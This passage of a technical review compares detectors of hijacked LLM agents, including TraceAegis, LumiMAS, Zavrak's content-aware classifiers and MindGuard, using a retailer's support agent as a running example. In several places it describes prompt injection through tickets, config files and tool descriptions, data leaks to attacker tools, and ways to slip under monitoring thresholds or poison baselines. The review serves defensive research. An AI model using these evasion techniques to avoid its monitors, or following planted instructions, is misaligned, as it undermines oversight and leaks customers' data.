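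Suppose three features describe a session: its number of calls, its duration and its amount of text, each scaled to lie between 0 and 1. The model reconstructs a harmless session of (0.2, 0.3, 0.2) as (0.2, 0.3, 0.3), a mean squared error of 0.003, and a hijacked session of (0.9, 0.3, 0.8) as (0.3, 0.3, 0.3), an error of 0.20.

This method can catch an unusual combination, such as a long session with very little text, even when each value is normal alone. But an alert that shows only "0.20" is hard to act on. The analyst has to check which features came back wrong, here the calls and the text, and then work out why.

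### TraceAegis: execution structure and conditions

Liu and colleagues built TraceAegis to learn the order of an agent's tool calls and the conditions under which each order makes sense. One of their two test agents directs patients to hospital departments. It looks up the accepted symptom keywords, uses a triage tool to find which departments to recommend, and fetches a checklist from each department.

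TraceAegis first arranges the tools in levels by their order in harmless traces. Tools that appear in either order, such as the orthopaedics and psychiatry checklists, share a level. TraceAegis next splits each trace into short units, so the trace of a patient who needs both departments becomes one unit for orthopaedics and another for psychiatry. A language model then summarises the conditions for each unit, for example that knee or arm pain leads to orthopaedics.

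TraceAegis flags a new trace if any of its units is unfamiliar. If all the units are familiar, a language model compares their content with the learned conditions. If the agent sent a patient with foot pain to the ear, nose and throat department, the trace would fail this second check even though the order of calls was normal.

The second test agent submits purchase requests for a car manufacturer. Half of each agent's 300 abnormal traces had unfamiliar sequences, caused by requests outside the agent's job or by malicious tool responses. The other half had familiar sequences with the wrong content.

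For each agent, the published scores are consistent with a test on the 300 abnormal traces and only 300 of the 1,300 harmless ones. Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026), in *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, also put the share of abnormal cases at about half. TraceAegis is compared with the same language models judging the traces without it. The false positive rates below are calculated from the published precision and recall, assuming each test used 300 harmless traces.

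| Agent and language model | Model alone: recall / false positive rate | TraceAegis: recall / false positive rate |
|---|---:|---:|
| Clinic, GPT-OSS-120B | 77.7% / 2.0% | 97.0% / 7.7% |
| Clinic, DeepSeek-V3 | 77.7% / 5.0% | 96.3% / 3.3% |
| Purchasing, GPT-OSS-120B | 49.0% / 2.3% | 93.3% / 6.0% |
| Purchasing, DeepSeek-V3 | 75.7% / 4.0% | 93.3% / 7.0% |

TraceAegis caught many more of the abnormal traces in all four tests, but raised more false alarms in three of them. Over 20 attacks and 10,000 harmless sessions, even its lowest false positive rate in the table, 3.3%, would give the retailer about 19 real alerts and 333 false ones, a precision of about 5%. With Gemini-2.0-Flash on the purchasing agent, the false positive rate was only about 1%, but TraceAegis missed about 14% of the abnormal traces, and the retailer would still get about 100 false alerts for 17 real ones. TraceAegis did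 much worse with a weaker language model, Gemma-3-27B, flagging about 36% of the harmless clinic traces.

In the purchasing test, TraceAegis detected all 150 unfamiliar sequences with every language model. It missed 20 of the 150 familiar sequences with the wrong content when using GPT-OSS-120B or DeepSeek-V3, and 86 when using Gemma. The attack in ticket 5120 would belong to this harder group.

The researchers also removed one part of the system at a time and compared F1 scores, which combine precision and recall. With DeepSeek-V3 on the clinic agent, the F1 score was 0.965 for the full system, 0.908 without the learned conditions and 0.756 without the levels. With GPT-OSS-120B, removing the levels lowered the score from 0.948 to 0.499, well below the 0.865 that the language model achieved alone. So much of the system's performance depends on the levels, and conditions that a language model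 derives from unsplit traces can make detection worse than using the model alone.

In a further test at a technology company, internal testers attacked an agent that looks for software vulnerabilities. In one attack, text hidden in a configuration file made the agent write its report before it had finished checking the code. TraceAegis flagged 132 of 140 altered sequences. The paper reports this as 94.3% accuracy, but the figure is recall, and the paper doesn't report how many of the company's ordinary sessions raised false alarms.

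All three agents follow a fairly fixed workflow, which suits a method based on levels, but the support agent might not. If it handles several tickets in one session, `read_ticket` comes both before and after `send_email`. The algorithm, as published, would then put all the tools on the same level, and TraceAegis would split the session into single calls and lose their order. The retailer could avoid this by first splitting the log at each ticket.

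Somebody also has to supply suitable traces for each agent. *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (2026) criticises TraceAegis for needing labelled templates for every scenario. Abbasi and colleagues add that the evaluation didn't test TraceAegis under changed conditions, such as new tools, though they only reviewed its protocol and did not run the detector. Errors in the traces could also last, because new traces can add relationships between tools but never remove them. If the training data included an attack, the detector would keep accepting that sequence of tool calls until somebody rebuilt the baseline.

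### LumiMAS: models of harmless event logs

*LumiMAS* (Solomon, Yerushalmi Levi and colleagues, 2026) uses autoencoders to monitor systems in which several agents work together. One autoencoder reconstructs operational measurements of each agent's run, such as duration, token count and number of tools used. A second works on numerical representations of the text the language models produce. A third combines the compressed outputs of the other two.

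The system therefore needs logs from inside the agents' runtime, while TraceAegis works from gateway records. The researchers collected more than 2,000 harmless runs for each of seven applications, including a trip planner and a property-research team. An agent that handles 20 tasks a day would take over three months to produce that many runs.

The test used 200 logs for each application, half of them containing a failure. Some failures were attacks and others were ordinary faults, such as made-up facts. The table gives recall and false positive rate for the five types in the paper's main results. It also includes LogBERT, an existing model that learns from the order of log events, for comparison.

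| Failure | Operational measurements | Text | Combined | LogBERT |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| Made-up facts | 64% / 13% | 63% / 20% | 65% / 12% | 42% / 41% |
| Biased answers | 63% / 46% | 67% / 44% | 65% / 33% | 89% / 87% |
| Malicious text in the user's request | 83% / 40% | 87% / 23% | 84% / 24% | 87% / 72% |
| Malicious web page | 97% / 9% | 91% / 9% | 94% / 6% | 97% / 5% |
| Poisoned reference database | 80% / 75% | 71% / 28% | 61% / 65% | 86% / 40% |

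The result for the malicious web page looks excellent, though LogBERT caught this attack slightly more often, with slightly fewer false alarms. Of these attacks, it is the most similar to the one in ticket 5120, but it left an obvious pattern in the log because the page lured the agent into following one deceptive link after another. An attack that needs only one ordinary-looking email would probably be much harder for either system to detect.

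Combining the two kinds of data didn't always improve detection. On the poisoned database, the combined model flagged harmless runs more often than attacked ones, while the text model alone did considerably better. A team that doesn't know which attack to expect can't choose the best model in advance.

The combined model averaged 76.8% recall and a 26.7% false positive rate, which would mean 2,670 false alarms over the retailer's 10,000 harmless sessions. Solomon and colleagues add a second layer, where a language model reads each flagged log and can dismiss it as harmless. They report that this cut false positives by about 60% on average, which would leave the retailer with roughly 1,070.

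The system also depends partly on known attacks. Its autoencoders learn only from harmless logs, but the researchers chose the alert threshold that gave the best F1 score on a separate set of 200 logs, half of which contained failures. A company without recorded attacks couldn't do this, and a threshold that works best when half the sessions are bad will usually be too low when one in 500 is.

LumiMAS's combined model took an average of 0.057 seconds per decision, while the fastest method that relied on a language model took more than 8 seconds. Some changes to an application, such as replacing a tool, require retraining, but that took about an hour of processor time.

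### How Exabeam extends user analytics to agents

Security companies already sell baselines of employee behaviour and are now extending them to agents. *Agent Behavior Analytics*, a July 2026 white paper from one of these companies, Exabeam, divides agents into three tiers by how closely they are integrated with a company's systems and how much they do on their own.

- Chatbots such as ChatGPT have no identity of their own in the company's systems. Exabeam keeps the baseline for the employee who uses them and looks for changes such as a jump in requests or in the amount of text processed.
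- Agents that work inside company systems often sign in with several service accounts and keys. Exabeam looks for unusual tool use and data access, but each account can appear as a separate entity.
- "Digital workers" have their own account in the company directory, as an employee would. Exabeam applies its ordinary user analytics to that account.

The retailer's support agent began in the middle group. A baseline for `svc_support`, the shared database account, would mix the support agent's reads with those of the returns agent and the nightly report. If the retailer gives the support agent its own account and uses it consistently, the agent moves into the last group, and its reads, tickets and emails can share one baseline. Exabeam says that linking several credentials to one agent is still in research and development, so the product can't yet fix this kind of identity problem by itself.

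Most of Exabeam's baselines need about 14 days of activity, though some rules need 7 or 28 days and others work immediately. An agent that exists for only an afternoon isn't around long enough for these baselines to form. Exabeam acknowledges this gap and partly covers it with rules that don't need a baseline.

Some of Exabeam's detections are simple, such as flagging the first time an employee successfully uses an agent's tool or creates an agent. Exabeam describes these signals as typically low in confidence and groups them into a case when several together exceed a risk threshold. In *AEBA*, written for Exabeam's competitor Securonix, Hunt says that a departure from the baseline can mean misuse or a legitimate change in how people use the agent.

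Exabeam's white paper illustrates its product with three attack scenarios, one of which relies partly on features still in development. It gives no recall or false positive rate for any of them. The eleven detector evaluations that Abbasi and colleagues audited don't provide these rates either, because none covers a commercial UEBA product. The white paper is therefore good evidence of what Exabeam's software measures, but not of how many attacks it detects.

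### An agent's own history and its peers

A baseline can come from the agent's own past or from similar agents, and the same behaviour can be normal by one baseline and abnormal by the other. Suppose the retailer runs a separate support agent in each of twelve countries.

On the Monday after a holiday, the German agent reads 270 records in an hour. Its past hours have a mean of 120 and a standard deviation of 30, so *z* is 5. But the other eleven agents have a mean of 260 and a standard deviation of 40 in the same hour. Compared with them, the German agent has a *z* of only 0.25, so the alert can probably wait.

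The Danish agent has had faulty instructions since its first day and opens five records for every ticket, so this looks normal against its own history. The other agents average 1.2 records per ticket with a standard deviation of 0.4, so the Danish agent's *z* against them is 9.5. Comparing an agent with its peers also helps when the agent is new and has no history.

Comparing an agent with its peers is less useful when the same cause affects them all. If an outside supplier changes the description of its parcel-tracking tool and all twelve agents start sending it customer data on the same morning, each will look normal beside the others. Only a comparison with earlier weeks would reveal the change. Peer groups must also contain agents that do similar work, since a returns agent and a support agent may behave differently for good reasons.

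### A proposed common format

*Agent Event Behaviour Analysis (AEBA)* (Sharif, 2026) proposes a shared format for agents' events, baselines and alerts that would combine both comparisons. Sharif submitted it as an individual in April 2026 to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops internet standards. It is an Internet-Draft, or working document, and no IETF stream has adopted it. The August version expires in February 2027 unless he renews it. Securonix uses the same initials for its own product category, "Agent and Entity Behavior Analytics", which is not an implementation of the draft.

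The draft requires a short-term baseline and a long-term one, and recommends 24 hours for the first and 90 days for the second. The long-term baseline is meant to catch baseline poisoning, in which an attacker changes an agent's behaviour so gradually that the baseline moves with it. For example, an attacker could start with an agent that reads 10 records a day and raise the number by 5% daily. After 60 days the agent would read about 187 records a day, yet each day would look only slightly busier than the one before. The 90-day average would still be about 45, so comparing the agent's current activity with it would reveal the change.

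Each event gets a score from 0 to 1 that combines the rate of events, the mix of activities, the likelihood of the chosen tool and agreement with the peer group. Sharif leaves the weights to whoever builds the software. Two products that follow the draft could therefore score the same call quite differently, which would make it hard to use the same threshold for both.

The April version illustrates the method with an invented shopping agent that normally pays around $40 at a time and makes 95% of its payments through one service. Planted text makes it attempt 15 payments of $5,000 in 30 seconds, through another service and to a new recipient. Almost any of the methods above would detect this, so the example is little evidence that the draft's method would catch subtler attacks. According to the draft itself, the method can't detect malicious behaviour that always stays within the baseline.

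One of its more practical ideas is to require a signed record whenever somebody deploys new code or changes the agent's model. An abrupt change in behaviour without such a record would then raise an alert.

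## Is metadata enough, or must the monitor read the content of calls?

Most of the baselines in the previous section need only metadata: which tools an agent called, in what order and how often. A company that logs nothing more avoids storing home addresses and private requests, but it may give up most of its chance of catching an attack like the one in ticket 5120. Sultan Zavrak of Duzce University tested this trade-off in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, published in May 2026.

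Zavrak trained detectors on the same sessions with and without the text of the calls. With metadata alone, a graph-based detector reached an AUROC of 0.640, not far above guessing. With the text, it reached 0.917, and a simpler method reached 0.975. This is good evidence that content matters for detecting the attacks in the main dataset, but weaker evidence about attacks in general, because that dataset's attacks work mainly by changing text.

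### How a session becomes numbers

The detector is meant to run beside a gateway and classify each session after its last call. It first turns the session into a graph, with one node for each call and a link between each call and the next. It also links two calls if text from the first one's response appears in the second one's arguments. This test is crude, because it looks for the first 50 characters of the response or for any of the response's first five words that is longer than four characters.

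Suppose `get_customer` returns a record that begins "Dana Holt, 18 Mill Lane". The word "Holt," counts as five characters with its comma, and the email's body also contains it, so the detector links the two calls. But the detector skips responses longer than 1,000 characters, so it would miss the link if a long order history pushed the record past that limit.

Each node then gets a list of numbers. In the metadata version, these encode the tool's name, the length of the response and a hash of the arguments. The hash can show that two calls had the same arguments, but not what they mean. This version still uses some content, because the hash and the data links come from the text. It also omits much of what a gateway logs as metadata, including the time, the caller and any refusals.

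In the content version, a small language model called a sentence encoder turns the arguments into a list of 384 numbers, called an embedding, and does the same for the response. Texts with similar meanings get similar embeddings. The encoder receives only the first 512 characters of each text, so an instruction planted further down a long ticket would not affect the embedding.

A graph neural network next updates each call's numbers using those of the calls linked to it:

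*hᵢ′* = *σ*(*f*(*hᵢ*, {*hⱼ* : *j* is linked to *i*}))

Here *hᵢ* is the list for call *i*, *f* is a function learned in training, and *σ* is a fixed non-linear function. The network does this twice, so information can travel two links.

Finally, the detector combines the calls' lists by taking the average and maximum at each position. If three calls had the lists (0.1, 0.9), (0.3, 0.5) and (0.8, 0.1), the averages would be 0.4 and 0.5 and the maxima 0.8 and 0.9. The classifier would receive only those four numbers, which don't show how many calls there were.

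Zavrak compared three graph networks (GraphSAGE, GCN and GAT) with an ordinary neural network that ignores the links. Zavrak also tried four older methods on the averaged and maximum embeddings: logistic regression, a linear support vector machine, and two methods that combine many decision trees (random forest and XGBoost).

### The main results

The main data come from *RAS-Eval* (Fu, Yuan and Wang, 2025), a benchmark of 80 tasks such as checking a calendar for events in a given hour. Eight language models carried out the tasks without interference, which gave Zavrak 605 usable harmless sessions. Another 3,797 sessions contain attacks, which replace a call's arguments, its response or both with prepared text.

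Zavrak trained each detector on 70% of the tasks, used 10% to decide when to stop training, and tested it on the remaining 20%. The figures are averages over three such splits.

| Detector | Input | AUROC | Recall | False positive rate |
|---|---|---:|---:|---:|
| GraphSAGE | Metadata | 0.640 | – | – |
| GraphSAGE | Content | 0.917 | 76.9% | 10.7% |
| Neural network without links | Content | 0.896 | 77.3% | 14.3% |
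| Logistic regression | Content | 0.917 | 86.5% | 12.8% |
| Random forest | Content | 0.974 | 96.6% | 19.1% |
| XGBoost | Content | 0.975 | 92.7% | 7.1% |

The graph contributed little, since logistic regression, a very simple classifier, matched the best graph network without using the links between calls. By contrast, removing the ordered levels from TraceAegis badly hurt detection. The difference is probably due to the attacks, since half of TraceAegis's abnormal traces had an unfamiliar order of calls, while RAS-Eval's attacks substitute text inside calls.

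For the same reason, the low metadata score is partly due to the benchmark. If an attacker changes a file path and the agent calls the same tools as before, a list of tool names shows almost no sign of the attack. Ticket 5120 would be just as hard to detect from tool names, but attacks that add calls leave at least some trace in the metadata.

The score of 0.640 is also uncertain, with a standard deviation of 0.106 across the three divisions. One table lists it under GraphSAGE and another under GAT, though the content version scores at least 25 points higher either way. Zavrak writes that metadata detection stays near 0.64 whatever the architecture, but the paper gives no metadata score for XGBoost or random forest, the two methods that did best with content.

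### Recognising the task instead of the attack

Zavrak's most useful finding for readers of other papers on this subject is an error in how researchers evaluate detectors. They usually split sessions between training and testing at random, so sessions from the same task end up in both sets, and a detector can score well by recognising the task.

With a random division, the same metadata detector's AUROC rose from 0.640 to 0.898. The content detector's AUROC (GAT in this comparison) rose from 0.891 to 0.992.

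The design of RAS-Eval suggests why recognising the task helps so much. Fu and colleagues wrote two attacks for each tool and combined them in every possible way, so a task that uses *n* different tools can have up to 2²ⁿ − 1 attacked versions, which is 3 for one tool and 63 for three. But each task has at most about eight harmless sessions, one for each language model.

With one task of each kind and 8 harmless sessions per task, there are 66 × 16 = 1,056 pairs of an attack and a harmless session. A detector that gives every session of the three-tool task a high score and every session of the one-tool task a low one would rank 504 pairs correctly, tie on 528 and get 24 wrong. Counting each tie as half, its AUROC would be (504 + 264)/1,056 = 0.73, even though its scores depend only on the task.

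Other research confirms that metadata can identify a task or an agent quite well. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026) reports that a system called AgentPrint identified which agent had produced a stream of encrypted traffic with an F1 score of 0.866, and that in a separate benchmark, tasks could be recognised from a single agent's traffic. So a company that stores only metadata can still learn a good deal about what its employees ask agents to do. But identifying the task doesn't reveal whether the agent is leaking data, such as a customer's address, while it answers a support ticket.

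### Why 0.975 may be too high

Zavrak's split puts different tasks in the training and test data, but the same attack texts can appear in both. Fu and colleagues wrote only 58 groups of attack templates, two for each of 29 tools, and the 80 tasks share those tools. A detector tested on an unseen task may therefore be given attack text that was in its training data. XGBoost may have learned partly to recognise these 58 groups, which would be much easier than recognising a new attack. Zavrak's paper doesn't discuss this problem. A fair test would keep some templates out of the training data.

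The attacked sessions also all come from one language model, GLM-4-Flash, while the harmless ones come from eight. If the harmless sessions are spread evenly across those eight models, a detector that perfectly recognised GLM-4-Flash's style would rank every attack above seven-eighths of the harmless sessions and level with the rest. Its AUROC would be 7/8 + 1/16, or about 0.94, again without using any sign of an attack. Zavrak found that metadata couldn't identify the model, but acknowledges that the embeddings might. There were too few harmless GLM-4-Flash sessions to test this properly.

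Only about 14% of the sessions are harmless. Each test uses a fifth of the tasks, which includes roughly 120 harmless sessions, so XGBoost's false positive rate of 7.1% is based on about nine false alarms per test. The true rate could easily be half or twice as high, and even 7.1% would give the retailer a heavy load of false alarms.

Zavrak's detectors also need labelled attacks, unlike the baselines in the previous section. A graph network's AUROC on RAS-Eval fell from 0.944 with all the labels to 0.800 with a tenth of them. Even that tenth includes around 300 attacked sessions, and few companies have recorded that many attacks on their agents. Training the network first on harmless sessions, which a company could do with its own logs, generally didn't reduce the number of labels it needed.

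Finally, the detector works only on finished sessions. This suits an audit or an investigation, but the support agent will have sent the email before its session ends.

### Small changes are hard to detect

For one of the three divisions, Zavrak broke down GraphSAGE's recall by the part of the call that the attack had changed:

| What the attack changed | Sessions | Recall |
|---|---:|---:|
| Arguments and response | 527 | 86.9% |
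| Response only | 77 | 81.8% |
| Arguments only | 57 | 36.8% |

The last figure is based on only 57 sessions, 21 of which count towards it, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 25% to 50%. Still, the paper's explanation is convincing. If an attacker replaces one file path or document number with another, the embedding barely changes.

Ticket 5120 has the same difficulty. The harmful call to `get_customer` contains `c-20931` instead of `c-18804`, and a sentence encoder will probably give the two nearly the same embedding. The earlier rule that compares the customer with the ticket's author would catch the difference, so embeddings may not be the best way for a company to monitor the text of calls.

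### A harder dataset

On a second dataset, *ATBench*, random forest had the best AUROC, at only 0.784, with 61.3% recall and a 21.1% false positive rate. Zavrak calls both datasets "real-world", but the 1,000 sessions in *ATBench* never took place on a real system. Li, Luo and colleagues (2026) used language models to simulate the user's requests, the tool calls and the responses, and five human reviewers then checked the results.

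ATBench is still the better test in one respect. Its safe and unsafe sessions come in pairs built from the same scenario, so a detector cannot tell them apart by recognising the task. In some of the safe sessions, the agent meets an attack and resists it. A detector that reacts to malicious text would flag these too, which the benchmark would count as false alarms, though a security team might well want to know about the attempted attacks.

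Li and colleagues gave whole sessions to large language models and asked them whether each session was safe. The false positive rates here are calculated from the published precision and recall.

| Detector on ATBench | Recall | False positive rate |
|---|---:|---:|
| Random forest on embeddings | 61.3% | 21.1% |
| Gemini-3-Flash | 71.0% | 18% |
| GPT-5.4 | 87.1% | 40% |
| AgentDoG-Qwen3-4B, a specialised safety model | 88.9% | 61% |

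The comparison is rough, since the random forest was trained on other ATBench sessions and tested on only about 200. The language models could also read the user's request, which a gateway usually doesn't have. Even with full access to the text, none of them could reliably separate the safe sessions from the unsafe ones. These models date from early 2026 or before, and newer ones may do better.

Zavrak reports no metadata score for ATBench, so the comparison between metadata and content rests on RAS-Eval alone. There appears to be no independent replication. Abbasi and colleagues note that the study never trained a detector on one dataset and tested it on another. Its highest AUROC, 0.986, came from pooling several sources, one of which contained only harmless sessions, so the classifier could score higher by recognising which source a session came from.

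Neither dataset closely matches ticket 5120, in which every call looks harmless by itself. *ChainWatch*, which proposes a detector that combines metadata with content, reports that no existing benchmark contains labelled sessions of this kind. Its own evaluation consists of five attacks from the literature, worked through on paper.

### Two classifiers for OpenTelemetry traces

Zavrak's review of earlier work cites a detector that wrongly flagged 66.7% of harmless traces. The figure, which represents 10 of 15 traces, comes from Del Rosario (2026), *Temporal Attack Pattern Detection in Multi-Agent AI Workflows*. Zavrak lists the detector as XGBoost or random forest, but Del Rosario adapted a language model with 8 billion parameters.

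The adapted model had to label 30 traces as benign, suspicious or malicious. It labelled 9 of the 15 attacks and 10 of the 15 harmless traces malicious, and the other 11 traces suspicious. If the retailer treated "suspicious" as an alert, recall and the false positive rate would both be 100%.

This detector could read the arguments of each call, so missing content did not cause its failure. Del Rosario blames the training data, an estimated 90% of which concerned attacks. The model had apparently learned to treat any series of steps as a threat. It flagged an agent that queried a database, made a PDF and emailed the report, which is close to what the retailer's agent does for the courier. But when a session read a file of system accounts and sent it to `attacker.com`, the model rated it only as suspicious. The same model had correctly answered 74% of a set of multiple-choice questions on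 security, so a good score on such questions is weak evidence that a model can read logs well.

Pathak, Kumar and colleagues report much better results in *Detecting Silent Failures in Multi-Agentic AI Trajectories* (2025). They trained XGBoost on 16 features of each trace, including token counts, durations and the number of tools used. It classified 98% of traces correctly for a stock-market assistant and 95% for a research assistant. A method that learned only from normal traces was correct for 96% and 90%. The features include some information about prompts, but counts of tools and steps mattered most, so metadata appears to have worked well here.

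However, the study was about faults, and its definition of a fault favours methods that count calls. A trace was abnormal if it contained an error, departed from the expected path, or used any agent or tool more than once. About half of the abnormal traces contained such a repeat, which a program can detect by comparing the number of calls with the number of different tools. Under the rule against repeats, any session in which the retailer's agent answered two tickets would be abnormal.

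The assistants also ran each prompt with several models and sets of instructions. The paper doesn't mention keeping all runs of a prompt together in either the training set or the test set, so the result may partly reflect the task recognition that Zavrak measured. The abnormal traces that XGBoost missed tended to be short, with a wrong step but no loop or error, as the trace for ticket 5120 would be.

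### MindGuard: looking inside the model

Even the full content of a call does not establish why the agent made it. *MindGuard* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) tries to determine this from the model's internal computations.

Their detector looks for altered tool descriptions. Suppose the retailer's parcel-tracking tool has a new description that tells the model to copy every email to an outside address. The agent can obey without calling the tracking tool. A full log would still include the email and its recipient, so the paper goes too far in saying that such attacks leave "no behavioral trace to monitor". But the log wouldn't show that the tracking tool's description had caused the call.

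Language models compute attention weights, which determine how strongly each piece of earlier text influences the next piece the model writes. MindGuard filters and combines these weights into one number for the user's request and one for each tool's description. For every tool that the agent did not call, it then calculates

*α* = weight of the uncalled tool / (weight of the user's request + weight of the called tool)

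If the tracking tool had a weight of 0.6, the user's request 0.5 and `send_email` 0.3, *α* would be 0.6/0.8 = 0.75. If a tool's *α* exceeds a chosen threshold, MindGuard raises an alert and treats that tool as the suspect.

It caught 97.1% of the hijacked calls with Qwen3-8B, a small open model, at a threshold of 0.5. It falsely flagged 1.5% of calls when no tool description was malicious, and 13.1% of normal calls made while a malicious description was present but had no effect. At a threshold of 0.9, it caught 91.2% of the hijacked calls, and the two false positive rates fell to zero and 0.9%. The test for this model included only 68 hijacked calls. Across the models tested, average precision, which summarises precision over all levels of recall, was 94% to 99% when the harmless calls came from clean data and 82% to 98% when a malicious description was present throughout.

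These results are impressive, though not directly comparable with Zavrak's, which cover different attacks and data. The main obstacle is that MindGuard needs the model's attention weights, which a company using a commercial model over the internet normally doesn't get. Wang and colleagues expect it to be used mainly by model providers or by organisations that run open models themselves. They also concede that an attacker might find wording that changes the model's decision but receives low attention weights, and they leave attacks that unfold over several turns to future work.

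### Where metadata may still be enough

Metadata can show bulk access. In the theft of 60 records described earlier, the number of calls to `get_customer` was unusual whatever the records contained. A sudden jump in response size can also reveal a large export made in a single call. Zavrak's low score isn't evidence against such checks, because the detector averaged over the calls in each session, which discards their number, and RAS-Eval's attacks don't involve unusual volume.

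A monitor can also spot a forbidden or unfamiliar tool by its name. *Log-To-Leak* (2026) describes an attack that makes an agent send its data to an attacker's logging tool after finishing the user's task. The user's answer looks much as usual, but the extra call appears in the list of calls, and a gateway with a list of approved tools could refuse it. A simple rule is safer here than a trained classifier. Abbasi and colleagues point out that a detector that counts calls to known tools will represent a session that uses only new tools as a row of zeros.

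A monitor can also detect loops, repeated errors and refused calls without reading content, and Pathak and colleagues' results suggest that metadata catches the first two well. Metadata may also expose a stolen key if calls arrive at odd hours or from a new address, although none of these studies tested that. Failures to act are harder to detect from metadata. *Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* (2026) observes that the shape of a run hardly changes when an agent skips a check it should have made.

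To detect an attack that uses the agent's usual tools in their usual order, the monitor has to read some of the content, but perhaps not all of it, because meta-information about the task can replace some of the text. Abbasi and colleagues describe a monitor called AlignmentCheck that gives a language model the user's request and the agent's calls with their arguments, but not the tools' responses. The model checks whether the latest call serves a goal that the user never set. Because it doesn't see the responses, text planted in a ticket can't mislead it directly.

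The retailer could go further and have the gateway read the content, since it already handles the full text of each call. The gateway could check whether the customer number matches the ticket's author and whether the email is addressed to that author, then send only the two results to the SIEM.

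## Why is it hard to set a baseline for an agent?

A monitor that uses metadata to flag bulk access needs a baseline for how many records an agent usually reads. That number may be steady enough to use if the agent does only one job. When an agent does whatever an employee asks, the number depends on the request, the model and the settings, so the average can be far from the actual number in almost every session.

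Security researchers had this difficulty long before agents existed. In *Outside the Closed World* (2010), Robin Sommer and Vern Paxson asked why companies rarely used machine learning to detect network intrusions, despite the many systems researchers had published. They argued that machine learning is better at finding things that resemble its training examples than at finding something new. Even basic features of network traffic, such as bandwidth and the mix of applications, vary so much over seconds or hours that a departure from the average may mean nothing. They also described a "semantic gap" between detecting that something is unusual and knowing whether it is harmful, which is what the operator needs. They advised targeting a narrow kind of attack and having a good reason to think the chosen feature will reveal it.

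All of this applies to agents, but a company can put an agent through the same task fifty times before anyone uses it, which it can't do with its employees. It can also log the request in plain language, while network packets seldom show what a user wanted. However, a new model can change the agent's behaviour in every session overnight, whereas a thousand network users rarely change their habits on the same day.

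### Narrow agents and general agents

An agent built for one purpose may well behave more regularly than a person. The baseline for an employee's account has to include covering for a sick colleague, changing jobs and working late before a deadline. The clinic agent in TraceAegis's tests follows much the same steps for every patient. Liu and colleagues credit their detector's advantage over plain language models to checking stable units of this kind.

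A general assistant has no fixed routine. It may summarise contracts on Monday and repair a spreadsheet on Tuesday because two people asked for different things. Its history mostly reflects what people have asked it to do, so a new user with a new kind of work will make it look abnormal.

Some evidence supports this distinction. *Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability* (Rabanser, Kapoor and colleagues, 2026) tested 15 models on two benchmarks, running each task five times. One benchmark has 26 simulated customer-service tasks for an airline, and the other has 165 open-ended questions that may require web searches, files or code. The agents were generally more consistent on the airline tasks, probably because these leave fewer ways to proceed, though the benchmarks also differ in other respects. The study didn't test people on the same tasks, so the idea that a narrow agent is more regular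 than an employee is plausible but unmeasured.

### The same task, run again

Even a narrow agent doesn't behave exactly the same way every time. Language models normally generate text partly at random, and one early difference can lead to a different series of tool calls. Developers can turn off this deliberate randomness in many models by setting the temperature parameter to zero. Rabanser and colleagues did so where they could and still found variation, which they attributed to causes such as rounding in parallel arithmetic and the load on the provider's servers.

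*How Consistent Are LLM Agents?* (Yagubyan, 2026) measured the variation in tool calls. Six models each carried out 19 office tasks ten times, which gave 1,140 traces. These were tasks such as finding a contact and sending an email, or checking a calendar for conflicts. The ten tools were simulated and always returned the same result for the same input, so any variation came from the models.

The study compares the tool sequences of two runs with

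similarity = 1 − (edits needed to turn one sequence into the other / length of the longer one)

Suppose the retailer's support agent calls `read_ticket`, `get_customer` and `send_email` in one run, then makes the same calls in another run but repeats `get_customer`. The sequences differ by one edit, and the longer one has four calls, so their similarity is 0.75. Yagubyan found an average similarity of 0.87, and ten runs of one task produced between 1.6 and 3.3 different sequences on average, depending on the model. An attack that adds one call to the agent's usual three scores the same 0.75 as the harmless repeat.

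Arguments varied more. Yagubyan divided the number of argument values that two runs shared by the number of distinct values across both runs, and the average was 0.69. For vague requests such as "Help me prepare for my meetings tomorrow", it fell to 0.52. Most of this variation was harmless, such as differently phrased searches or "alice" instead of "Alice", and it didn't predict whether agents completed the task correctly.

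Comparing runs by the proportion of values they share is a problem for security. If two runs send an email with the same recipient and subject but different text, they share two of four distinct values and score 0.5. They also score 0.5 if the subject and text are the same but an attacker has changed the recipient. A baseline therefore has to treat the recipient's address differently from the wording of the message.

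Yagubyan found that 60% of differences between runs began in the first two calls, and suggests comparing just those calls with a reference run. This may be an efficient way to find runs that are going wrong, but it is poorly suited to finding prompt injection, because the agent has to read the planted text before following it. In ticket 5120, for example, the first two calls use the usual tools in the usual order.

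In *When Agents Disagree With Themselves*, Mehta (2026) found similar variation in a simpler setting. Four models answered each of 200 questions ten times and could only search, retrieve a text or give an answer. Claude Sonnet 4.5 took an average of 2.3 different sequences of actions per question, and Llama 3.1 70B took 4.2. Models were correct 82% to 87% of the time on questions where they took at most two different sequences, and 41% to 65% of the time where they took four or more. An odd series of calls may therefore only mean that the question was hard for the agent.

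Most of these models are now old, and the exact figures may not hold for newer ones. But Rabanser and colleagues tested GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.7, among others, and found that more capable models were not reliably more consistent. Larger models were often less consistent than smaller ones, perhaps because they can do a task in more ways. They also found that agents repeated the same mix of actions much more reliably than the same order. A baseline that counts calls of each type should therefore be steadier than one that scores sequences, though it will miss attacks that change only the order.

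### Mixed tasks

Differences between tasks can be much larger than differences between runs. Suppose 90% of an agent's tasks take 4 calls and 10% take 40. The mean is 7.6 calls and the standard deviation is 10.8, so an alert at three standard deviations above the mean requires more than

7.6 + 3 × 10.8 = 40 calls

If an attack causes the agent to make 35 calls during a short task, nearly nine times the normal number, the session passes unnoticed because its score is only 2.5.

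The result doesn't depend on the long tasks taking 40 calls. If a share *p* of tasks is long and all long tasks take the same number of calls, their score is

*z* = √((1 − *p*)/*p*)

At *p* = 10%, this is exactly 3. If the long tasks took 400 calls, the threshold would rise to 400. Occasional long tasks therefore let an attacker add calls to any short task without crossing the threshold.

*Measuring Cross-Task Behavioral Consistency in Language Model Agents* (2026) reports that an agent can be consistent when it repeats a task and still lack a consistent strategy across different tasks. Testing an agent on one task at a time won't reveal this inconsistency.

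A crude baseline can catch an attack that causes a large jump in calls. Pillar Security's *Missing Agent-Specific Anomaly Detection*, a security vendor's description of the risk, gives the example of a coding agent that normally makes 5 calls per session but makes 200 after an attacker takes it over. Even the mixed baseline above would give 200 calls a score of nearly 18. The example supports having some baseline for each agent, but it doesn't cover the sessions with 35 calls.

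### A new model or a new setting

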